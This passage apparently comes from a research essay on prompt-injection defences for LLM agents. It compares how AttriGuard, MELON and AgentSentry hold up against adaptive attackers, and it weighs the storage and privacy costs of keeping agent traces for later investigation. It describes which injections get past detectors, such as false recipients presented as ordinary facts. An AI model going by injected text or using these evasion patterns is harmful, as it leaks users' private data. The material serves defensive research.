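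Fixed attacks can make a detector, like a model, look stronger than it is. He et al. tested AttriGuard against a simulated attacker who knew how it worked, could see its reactions and had 200 attempts at each of 61 tasks. They used a stricter setting than in their main experiments. The attacker succeeded in four tasks on Gemini and six on Llama. Raising the limit to 500 attempts on Gemini produced no further successes. On the same Gemini tasks, MELON, another defence that runs the agent a second time, stopped every fixed attack but failed against the simulated attacker in 82% of tasks.

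Few real attackers would have this much information, so the test was harsher than what most deployments would face. The attacks that got past AttriGuard all pursued a goal that could pass for a useful part of the user's task. In such cases, the agent may make the call without being steered by the injected text, which leaves little influence for a test of what caused the call to detect.

Zhang and colleagues tried 36 attack variants aimed at AgentSentry's mechanism. Of the 19 that worked on an undefended agent, two also worked on an agent defended by AgentSentry. Both presented a false recipient as an ordinary fact, as in Yu and colleagues' example of the doctor's address. AgentSentry looks for passages that try to control the agent and does not check whether the other passages are true. Comparing the address with a trusted company record could catch this attack, if such a record exists and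 the attacker cannot edit it.

### The cost of keeping full traces

Detectors can read only what the company records. Wang, Sun and colleagues (2026) reviewed 90 studies of agent logs in *Log Analysis for LLM-Based Agents*. They found that recording methods usually keep the inputs and results of each operation, but less often the permissions behind it or the agent's reasoning. Most methods record from inside the agent's software. Recording at a gateway can cover activity that these methods miss, but it usually captures less about what the agent was trying to do.

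Storing the text may not take much space. In Zhang and colleagues' tests, a harmless task used about 4,700 tokens on average without a defence. At roughly four bytes per token, 200,000 such tasks a day would produce nearly 4 gigabytes daily, or about 1.4 terabytes a year before compression. Long email threads and attachments could make the total many times larger, but storage is unlikely to be the main obstacle for a company running that many agent tasks.

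Privacy is a more serious problem. The trace of Dana's task would include the supplier's message and her colleague's note about the price limit, which is the figure the attacker wanted. Anyone with access to the trace could read that note without permission to open Dana's mailbox. A central store of traces would collect such material from every employee who uses an agent, making it an attractive target. Wang and colleagues also describe research in which private data appeared in messages between agents but not in their final answers, so a trace may contain more private data than its users expect.

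Some detectors create further copies of the data an agent reads. AttriGuard sends tool results to a second model for rewriting. In He and colleagues' tests, that model was OpenAI's GPT-4.1-mini, even when the agent ran on another company's model. A company that used such a mixed setup to process Dana's emails would be sharing them with a second provider.

A company can limit these risks by restricting access to traces and deleting them early. AttriGuard and AgentSentry need the text only while a task is running, so they don't require long-term storage. TraceAegis has to keep past calls and results long enough to learn from them. A company could also store just the recipient of each email, the source of that address and a digital fingerprint of the body. These would show that Dana's assistant emailed an address from the supplier's message. But an investigator who learned of the leak six months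 later would need the message itself to find the planted instruction, because a fingerprint can only confirm that a surviving copy is genuine.
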